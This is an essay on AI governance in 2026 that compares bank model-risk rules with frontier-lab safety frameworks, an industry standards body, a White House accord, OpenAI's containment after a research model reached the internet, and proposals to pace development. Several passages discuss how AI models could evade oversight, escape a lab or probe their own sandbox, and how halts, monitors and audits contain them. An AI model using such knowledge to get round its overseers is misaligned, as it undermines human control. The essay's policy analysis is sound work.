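Until 17 April 2026, the main US guidance on banks' models was a 2011 letter known as SR 11-7. The banking agencies then replaced it with the Federal Reserve's *Revised Guidance on Model Risk Management* (2026), or SR 26-2, which does not cover generative AI or AI agents. The accompanying bulletin, the OCC's *Model Risk Management* (2026), explains that they are excluded because they are "novel and rapidly evolving".

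The guidance also excludes deterministic rule-based software that has no statistical, economic or financial theory behind it, which presumably describes most spending caps and policy engines. So of the things relevant to Ayoub's comparison, the guidance covers a bank's value-at-risk model, but not an AI agent or the simple rules that constrain it. The guidance isn't enforceable, and supervisors won't criticise a bank for failing to follow it.

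The law firm Sullivan & Cromwell notes, however, that banks' use of generative AI and agents remains subject to the general expectations about risk management and governance. The OCC's November framework partly fills the gap. It applies mainly to generative AI and agents, and uses the administration's new term for AI, "super intelligence". It starts with a written statement of what an agent may do, then covers controls, oversight, recovery from failures and evidence that the controls still work.

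A bank that wanted to build a perimeter could use much of this, but the wording is cautious. Controls "could" increase with the consequences of a failure, and riskier uses "may" warrant tighter restrictions. According to Morrison Foerster's *OCC Issues Supervisory Framework for Bank Use of Super Intelligence* (2026), the document sets no supervisory expectations for banks. The market access rule for brokers, by contrast, is binding, and Knight paid a fine for breaking it. The agencies said in April that they would soon ask for information on how banks use AI, including agents. In September, *AGs warn Congress that AI threatens the financial system* (Pape, 2026) reported that state attorneys general want Congress to go further.

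## Who sets and checks the rules, and which risks lie outside one company

Containing AI means different things for different companies. A retailer wants to stop its purchasing agent from overspending. A laboratory such as Google DeepMind has to make sure that a new frontier model, one of the most capable in existence, doesn't help anyone build a weapon or escape its developers' control. Ayoub was probably addressing firms like the retailer, but he also named Google's policy on frontier models as part of the answer.

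If the retailer sets its spending cap too high, it mostly loses its own money, so it has a good reason to get the cap right. A laboratory's mistakes, however, may hurt people who have never dealt with it. The laboratory also can't fence in every agent built on its models, because its customers choose the tools and rules, and a criminal using a model to plan a cyberattack won't install a policy engine to block it.

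In finance, outsiders came to set some of the rules and inspect the results. A bank that uses AI agents still has outside supervisors who can ask about them, but a retailer usually has no comparable supervisor. AI laboratories have mostly written their own rules. *Common Elements of Frontier AI Safety Policies*, by the AI evaluation group METR, lists twelve developers that have published such policies, including Google DeepMind.

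### The thresholds in Google's framework

Google published the current edition of its policy, version 3.1 of Google DeepMind's *Frontier Safety Framework* (2026), on 17 April. It was still the newest when Ayoub spoke, according to *Google raises security to level 2+ for 3 types of dangerous AI* (Rijo, 2026). The framework covers only severe risks and some slightly lesser ones. It is built around critical capability levels, which are abilities that could heighten the risk of severe harm if Google took no precautions. The April edition added tracked capability levels, for harm that is significant but not severe.

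| Area | Level | What the model can do | Recommended security |
|---|---|---|---|
| Chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons | Tracked | Help people with low to medium resources enough to risk significant harm | Judged case by case |
| The same weapons | Critical | Help the same people enough to add severe harm | 2+ |
| Cyberattacks | Critical | Help with high-impact attacks enough to add severe harm | 2+ |
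| Manipulation (exploratory) | Critical | Systematically change people's beliefs and behaviour where the stakes are high | 2+ |
| Stealth and awareness of its situation | Tracked | Get around basic oversight so well that Google can't rule out a serious loss of human control | Judged case by case |
| Speeding up AI research | Critical | Make AI progress substantially faster than in the past | 3 |
| Automating AI research | Critical | Replace any Google team that works on improving AI, at similar cost | 4 |

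The research organisation RAND devised the security levels. They describe how well a developer protects a model's weights, the numbers that training produces, against theft or tampering. A thief who copies the weights can remove the model's safeguards, and the developer can't take the copy back. Google added level 2+, which has extra precautions against insiders and well-resourced criminals.

For a new frontier model, the process runs roughly like this:

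1. Google tests the model's dangerous abilities before releasing it outside the company. An alert threshold just below each critical level gives warning that a model may reach the level before the next full assessment.
2. If the model reaches an alert threshold, Google studies how close it is to the critical level and draws up a response plan.
3. If the model reaches a tracked or critical level, Google develops safeguards, such as training it to refuse certain requests, monitoring its use and verifying who its users are.
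4. Google estimates the risk that remains. At a critical level it must also write a safety case, an argument that outsiders could in principle assess, showing that the risk is acceptable.
5. What Google calls the "appropriate governance function" decides whether the risk is acceptable. Only then may the model go out.

This is a sensible process, but hardly any of it is a deterministic perimeter. A cash machine refuses any withdrawal over a set limit, whereas Google has to judge what counts as severe harm, how much a model adds to it and how much remains after the safeguards. Google acknowledges that these assessments are often partly subjective. The closest part to Ayoub's fence is a suggestion to limit what a model can access if it might undermine human control.

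The framework also gives Google several ways to relax its requirements. If a competitor has already released a similar model with few safeguards, Google may count its own release as adding little risk. Each decision may be reasonable, but if every laboratory reasons this way, the least careful one sets the standard. Brokers were in a similar position before checks on orders became compulsory.

Reaching a threshold does not by itself stop Google from training a stronger model, either. Google requires adequate security for the weights during further development. But the safeguards in step 3 apply only to releases and, for the risks from stealth and AI research, to high-risk internal uses.

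### Google as judge of its own thresholds

The framework does affect what Google releases. Digital Journal's *Google restricts access to new AI model over safety concerns* (2026) reports that on 30 September Google withheld its most powerful model, Gemini 4 Argon, from the public for the time being. Google's *Gemini 4 Argon Safety & Security Report* (2026), published the following month, covers independent outside testing for weapons, cyberattacks and manipulation. Google still decides what to do about the results.

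Google decides what counts as "substantially" faster progress in AI research, and if it concluded that a model had crossed that threshold, it would face a recommendation for more expensive security. In the October report, Google found that AI was automating some parts of AI research but had not significantly accelerated the work from end to end. On 29 November, The News International published *Google DeepMind chief credits AI betterment for faster Gemini releases*, in which Koray Kavukcuoglu, who now leads the laboratory, called AI's help in building its successors a major factor in recent gains. The two statements may be compatible, because AI can be a major factor without making progress "substantially" faster than before.

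Outsiders can't easily tell who at Google would make that decision. In the review *Google DeepMind’s Frontier Safety Framework v3.1*, a member of the research organisation GovAI welcomed the earlier thresholds and the tighter security. But the reviewer criticised the new one-paragraph section on governance for leaving out who is responsible for which decisions, who can block a release and what happens when teams disagree. The reviewer also noted that Google doesn't firmly commit to when it will bring in outside experts.

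These gaps became more important in August, when Google was preparing to move its "AI responsibility" unit from Google DeepMind to its global affairs organisation, which handles lobbying and public policy. PYMNTS's *Google Shifts AI Safety Unit out of DeepMind Lab to Global Affairs* (2026) attributed the news to the Wall Street Journal, which had seen an internal email. DIGITIMES's *Google moves AI safety team into global affairs in DeepMind overhaul* (2026) reported that about 90 people would move in early September as part of a wider reorganisation. Their work includes assessing Gemini's chemical, biological and nuclear risks, according to Darth Sahara's *Google выводит команду по оценке рисков ИИ из DeepMind* (2026), a report for a Russian technology site. Some people inside Google worried that the team would lose independence and become worse at spotting risks in new models.

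Bank supervisors expect the people who measure a risk to be independent of the people who take it. That standard gives some support to the move, because a team inside the laboratory answers to managers who want to release models. The pressure to release them was probably growing. The Straits Times' *Google shifts AI power to California in race against Anthropic, OpenAI* (2026) described a focus on quick results under Kavukcuoglu, after Hassabis moved to a chairman's role.

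But the team's new department lobbies governments, so it has an interest in not telling them that the company's latest model is dangerous. A bank that moved its risk managers from the trading floor to the press office would likewise separate them from the traders without making them independent. Being further from the laboratory could also make it harder for the team to see new models early and to understand them.

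Independence is also not enough without power. At Barings, the internal auditors' advice about Nick Leeson's double role changed nothing. The framework doesn't specify whether Google's 90 specialists, or anyone who listens to them, can stop a release.

### Hassabis's standards body

In July, Hassabis had proposed in *A Framework for Frontier AI and the Dawning of a New Age* that an outside body do part of this checking. His model was FINRA, the American brokers' regulator, which brokers fund and the SEC supervises. He argued that the United States should set up a similar body for frontier AI, funded mostly by the industry, with independent technical experts and representatives of open-source developers on its board.

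The body would decide which models count as frontier models, using benchmarks that it would keep up to date. It would test those models for dangerous abilities in areas such as cybersecurity and biology, and for deception and attempts to get around safeguards. Hassabis suggested renewing the tests about every three months at first. Eventually the body should write some tests in secret, so that laboratories can't train their models to pass them.

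Laboratories would at first volunteer their models for review up to 30 days before release. Once the tests proved reliable, every frontier model, wherever it was made, would have to pass them before anyone could offer it in the United States. Smaller models would be exempt. If the danger seemed great enough, the body could also coordinate a slowdown among the leading laboratories.

The idea quickly found supporters, including Microsoft's chief executive, Satya Nadella, and the head of its AI division, Mustafa Suleyman (Kahn, 2026, *A FINRA for AI?*). Sam Altman of OpenAI and Elon Musk both called the proposal thoughtful. David Sacks, a former White House adviser who generally opposes regulating technology, preferred it to direct government regulation. Bloomberg reported that the Trump administration was considering such a body under the SEC, and Hassabis hoped to launch it by the end of the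 year, according to Deutscher.

Critics doubt that FINRA is a good example to follow. Senator Elizabeth Warren has accused it of favouring the firms that pay its bills. Its former head of enforcement, Brad Bennett, said its fines are too low and that some large brokers find it cheaper to pay one occasionally than to comply. FINRA can also label high-risk brokers "restricted". The consulting firm SLCG found that it labelled no firms in the first year, although at least 13 seemed to deserve the label.

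Yoshua Bengio, a pioneer of modern AI who now runs a safety research organisation, accepted the practical case for starting with a voluntary system. But he wanted a precise plan for making it compulsory and independent audits of whether companies meet its standards. Hassabis gives a condition for making the system compulsory but no date, and someone would have to decide when the condition was met.

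ITPro's *Google DeepMind boss Demis Hassabis issues call to action on AI safety* also questioned why China would heed an American body. Access to American customers would give foreign companies a reason to comply, as it does in the drug industry. But Kahn points out that a government building a model for its own military wouldn't need those customers.

The proposal would test models before release, but it wouldn't inspect the rules that a retailer or hospital puts around an agent, and Ayoub's claim depends on those rules. An agent can delete a company's database even if its model has passed every test for weapons and deception. FINRA supervises the brokers who use trading software, so a regulator modeled more closely on it would also supervise companies that use AI.

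### The White House accord

The American government instead began with voluntary promises. On 29 September 2026, President Trump and six companies, Anthropic, Google, Meta, Nvidia, OpenAI and SpaceX, signed an accord on AI safety. Free Press Journal's *US President Donald Trump, Tech Giants Sign 'Morally Binding' Frontier AI Safety* (2026) describes four layers: technical controls, internal monitoring, independent audits and board oversight. *Trump's AI "constitution" crowns day of accelerating ambition* (Basu, 2026) sums up part of the terms as "police yourselves". The signatories called the accord "morally binding", so it has no legal force, though Congress could build on it later.

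The accord had no deadlines until officials met the companies on 3 December. The Jerusalem Post's *Trump's AI task force sets deadline for external auditor*, a Reuters report, lists them. By 31 December, each company will form an internal team and hire an outside auditor to monitor model safety, and announce how it plans to introduce its controls. By 31 January 2027, it will have minimum internal standards for the controls and aim to have an independent board committee meet to review compliance.

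The controls are meant to ensure that models "do not access digital or technical systems in unexpected ways", which is close to what Ayoub described. Fixed rules are fairly good at limiting what a model can reach. For example, a laboratory could block all connections from a training computer except those to a short list of addresses, and an auditor could check the list and try to get past the block.

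However, the companies will hire their auditors a month before their internal standards are due. An auditor who checks only whether a company follows its own standards may miss controls the company never thought of. Knight Capital's review before its accident had this weakness. A good auditor would ask what a model could still do if every listed control worked.

Stan (2026), in *White House says AI labs will hire auditors to ‘monitor model safety’*, notes that the auditors have no deadline for finishing their work. The accord also doesn't cover every company with a published frontier safety policy, since Microsoft and Amazon have them but did not sign alongside the six signatories. It still improves on purely internal checks because it brings an outsider into each company that signed. How much it improves on them will depend on what the auditors may see and whether anyone publishes their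 findings.

### OpenAI's own perimeter

OpenAI has already had to rebuild the containment around its own research. It stopped training and evaluating its most capable models from 20 September to 1 October 2026, after a research model gained limited access to the internet. Ayoub spoke in Amsterdam on the fourth day of that pause.

OpenAI described its new arrangements in *Managing frontier AI risk*, published in November 2026. It now trains frontier models with no live internet access, and its strongest models continually test the barriers for gaps. A central system can stop a job's output within 35 seconds of an order to halt. OpenAI also requires a safety case and reviews each model before moving it from research to internal use, and again before release.

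The history of trading supports some of this. At the rate Knight was losing money, a halt after 35 seconds would have limited its losses to about $6 million. But someone or something has to notice the problem and order the halt, and no halt is fast enough to stop a single harmful action like the deletion at PocketOS. Cutting off internet access protects better against such actions.

Having models search the barriers for gaps is a newer idea. It could continually test the barriers against an attacker about as capable as the model they contain, which no yearly inspection can do. But it relies on the models to report what they find, so OpenAI would be unwise to make it the only test.

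The episode supports part of Ayoub's claim, because OpenAI tightened its controls within days and the rules it added don't require anyone to understand the model. But OpenAI itself decided when to stop, what to fix and when the fix was good enough to start again. If a bank had been in the same position, a supervisor would probably have asked it for evidence.

### The case for pacing the frontier

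Some people who run laboratories, such as Anthropic's Dario Amodei, think that better fences won't be enough and also want to control the pace of development. In an essay published about a month before Hassabis's, Amodei suggested supervising AI much as the US Federal Aviation Administration supervises aviation, SiliconANGLE reported. According to Axios' *Behind the Curtain* (2026), Amodei wants a federal agency that can block model releases from the start, whereas Hassabis would begin with voluntary reviews by an industry-funded body.

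On 30 November, Altman and Greg Brockman of OpenAI proposed that laboratories agree on limits to how far AI may exceed human ability. A laboratory could pass each limit only after showing it had adequate safeguards, and the limits would change over time. According to The Next Web's *OpenAI wants limits on how much smarter than people AI can get*, Altman and Brockman would rather never build superintelligence, AI far beyond human ability, than give up human control.

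The best argument for pacing is that engineers design a fence around the abilities they know about. A more capable model may find a gap nobody has imagined, and its developers may learn of the ability only when the model uses it. Testing each model thoroughly before building the next would give them a chance to discover it earlier. Competition discourages this, because a laboratory that stops to test falls behind those that don't. Hassabis, whose own laboratory is one of the competitors, wrote that advances are "outpacing our understanding of the technology".

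The other part of the argument is that one company's fence can't protect people from another company's model. Suppose twelve developers each have a 1% chance per year of a failure that harms the public, and that the failures are independent. The chance of at least one is then

1 − 0.99¹² ≈ 11%.

If one developer is careless and has a 20% chance, the total rises to about 28%. Making the other eleven developers' fences perfect would only reduce the total to 20%. Bringing the careless developer up to the ordinary standard would reduce it to 11%. These numbers are invented, but they show why a careful laboratory might care more about a common limit than about improving its own controls. Google DeepMind acknowledges in its framework that some of its precautions protect society only if all the relevant organisations provide similar protection.

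Pacing also has serious drawbacks. It would delay whatever good the next models could do, and a limit might favour whichever companies were ahead when it took effect. It would also fail if a country outside the agreement carried on. An agreement among American laboratories could still gain time if they are well ahead, but the smaller their lead, the less time it would gain.

### A number to put the limit on

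A limit also needs a measure of capability. The one suggested by OpenAI's chief scientist, Jakub Pachocki, is perplexity, which captures how well a model predicts text. If a model gives the actual fragments of a text the probabilities *p*₁ to *p*ₙ, then

perplexity = (1 / (*p*₁ × *p*₂ × … × *p*ₙ))^(1/*n*).

Suppose a model gave the three fragments of a text probabilities of 1/2, 1/4 and 1/8. Their product is 1/64, and the cube root of 64 is 4, so the model's perplexity is 4. This is the same average uncertainty as in a choice among four equally likely fragments. A better predictor has a lower perplexity, so an agreement might forbid laboratories to go below a certain perplexity until they had shown that their safeguards were adequate.

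Perplexity is attractive as a measure because anyone with the model and the text can repeat the calculation and get the same answer. But Jared Kaplan of Anthropic replied on 4 December, in *Measuring model capabilities for pacing the frontier*, that it misses much of what makes a model capable. Kaplan also argued that laboratories could easily game the measure, and that using it would push them towards more reinforcement learning, a kind of training that rewards a model for succeeding at tasks. Such training can make an agent much better at its work but no better at predicting text. A laboratory that had reached the limit could therefore keep building more capable agents without breaking the agreement.

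Kaplan published Anthropic's own figures and offered to work on a better measure, so he wasn't rejecting the idea of limits. Banks had a similar difficulty with value at risk, but their supervisors could compare the estimates with actual losses over 250 trading days. Nobody has a comparable record of how dangerous frontier models turned out to be, and compiling one could require many harmful incidents.

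### Institutions and resilience

Sayash Kapoor, Rishi Bommasani and Arvind Narayanan put less weight on the frontier itself. In *The missing quadrant in responses to AI*, published in November 2026, they expect AI capabilities to keep improving quickly and the technology to transform society. But they argue that the pace of AI's effects will depend more on people and organisations than on capability. They want to reform institutions, and they call society's resilience the most neglected defence against AI risks.

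Resilience is the ability to withstand harm and recover. For example, a hospital that can treat patients for a week without its computers will suffer less from a cyberattack, whichever company's model helped the attacker. Resilience protects society roughly as capital protects a bank. It also helps against foreign and stolen models, which no agreement among laboratories can cover.

The disagreement with those who want to control the pace of frontier AI development depends largely on how much time there would be to respond to a failure. A firm may take years to reorganise its work around AI, which gives regulators and rivals time to respond. A criminal can use a new model the day it comes out, and a model that escapes from a laboratory could do harm without having any customers. Kapoor and colleagues take seriously the possibility that AI will automate AI research, but don't assume that this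 will end in superintelligence. Someone who thinks rapid progress towards superintelligence is likely has more reason to want to slow development, since a society can't prepare to recover from a permanent loss of control.

A government could combine these approaches by paying for better defences in hospitals and requiring laboratories to pass a review before building stronger models. Resilience is probably the safer investment for someone unsure which forecast is right, because it is useful in either case and doesn't depend on measuring capability.

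### Keeping up with exponential capability

Ayoub described the problem as capability growing exponentially while governance grows linearly. Google's framework partly addresses this by tying reviews to what a model can do instead of to the calendar. If capability doubles every year and each doubling triggers one review, there is one review a year however capable the models become, so linear governance can keep up. It falls behind if the doublings come faster, as they might if AI speeds up AI research, or if each review takes longer than the last.

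Suppose a laboratory takes a large step in capability every six months, and reviewing each step takes nine months. After three years the laboratory has taken six steps and reviewers have finished with three. After six years it has taken 12 and they have finished with seven, so the backlog has grown from three to five. Now suppose the laboratory may not take a step until reviewers have finished with the previous one. It takes only four steps in the first three years and eight in six, but at any time there is at most one step that hasn't been fully reviewed.

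Pacing is the only proposal here that removes the backlog by design. The body Hassabis proposes could also do this if it used its power to coordinate a slowdown, but its ordinary 30-day review helps only if 30 days is long enough. The accord sets deadlines for companies to introduce controls but lets them set the speed of development. OpenAI's automated testing is meant to speed up checking as model development speeds up. That might work well for finding holes in a sandbox, but it is less promising for deciding how much risk the public should bear.

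Pacing would therefore answer Ayoub's worry best, since one company's own perimeter can limit that company's agents but can't give everyone else more time. Pacing is also the least ready, however. The laboratories have not agreed on a measure, and an agreement would need someone to enforce it. Ayoub seems to have recognised part of this when he said that guardrails will need partnerships beyond technology companies.
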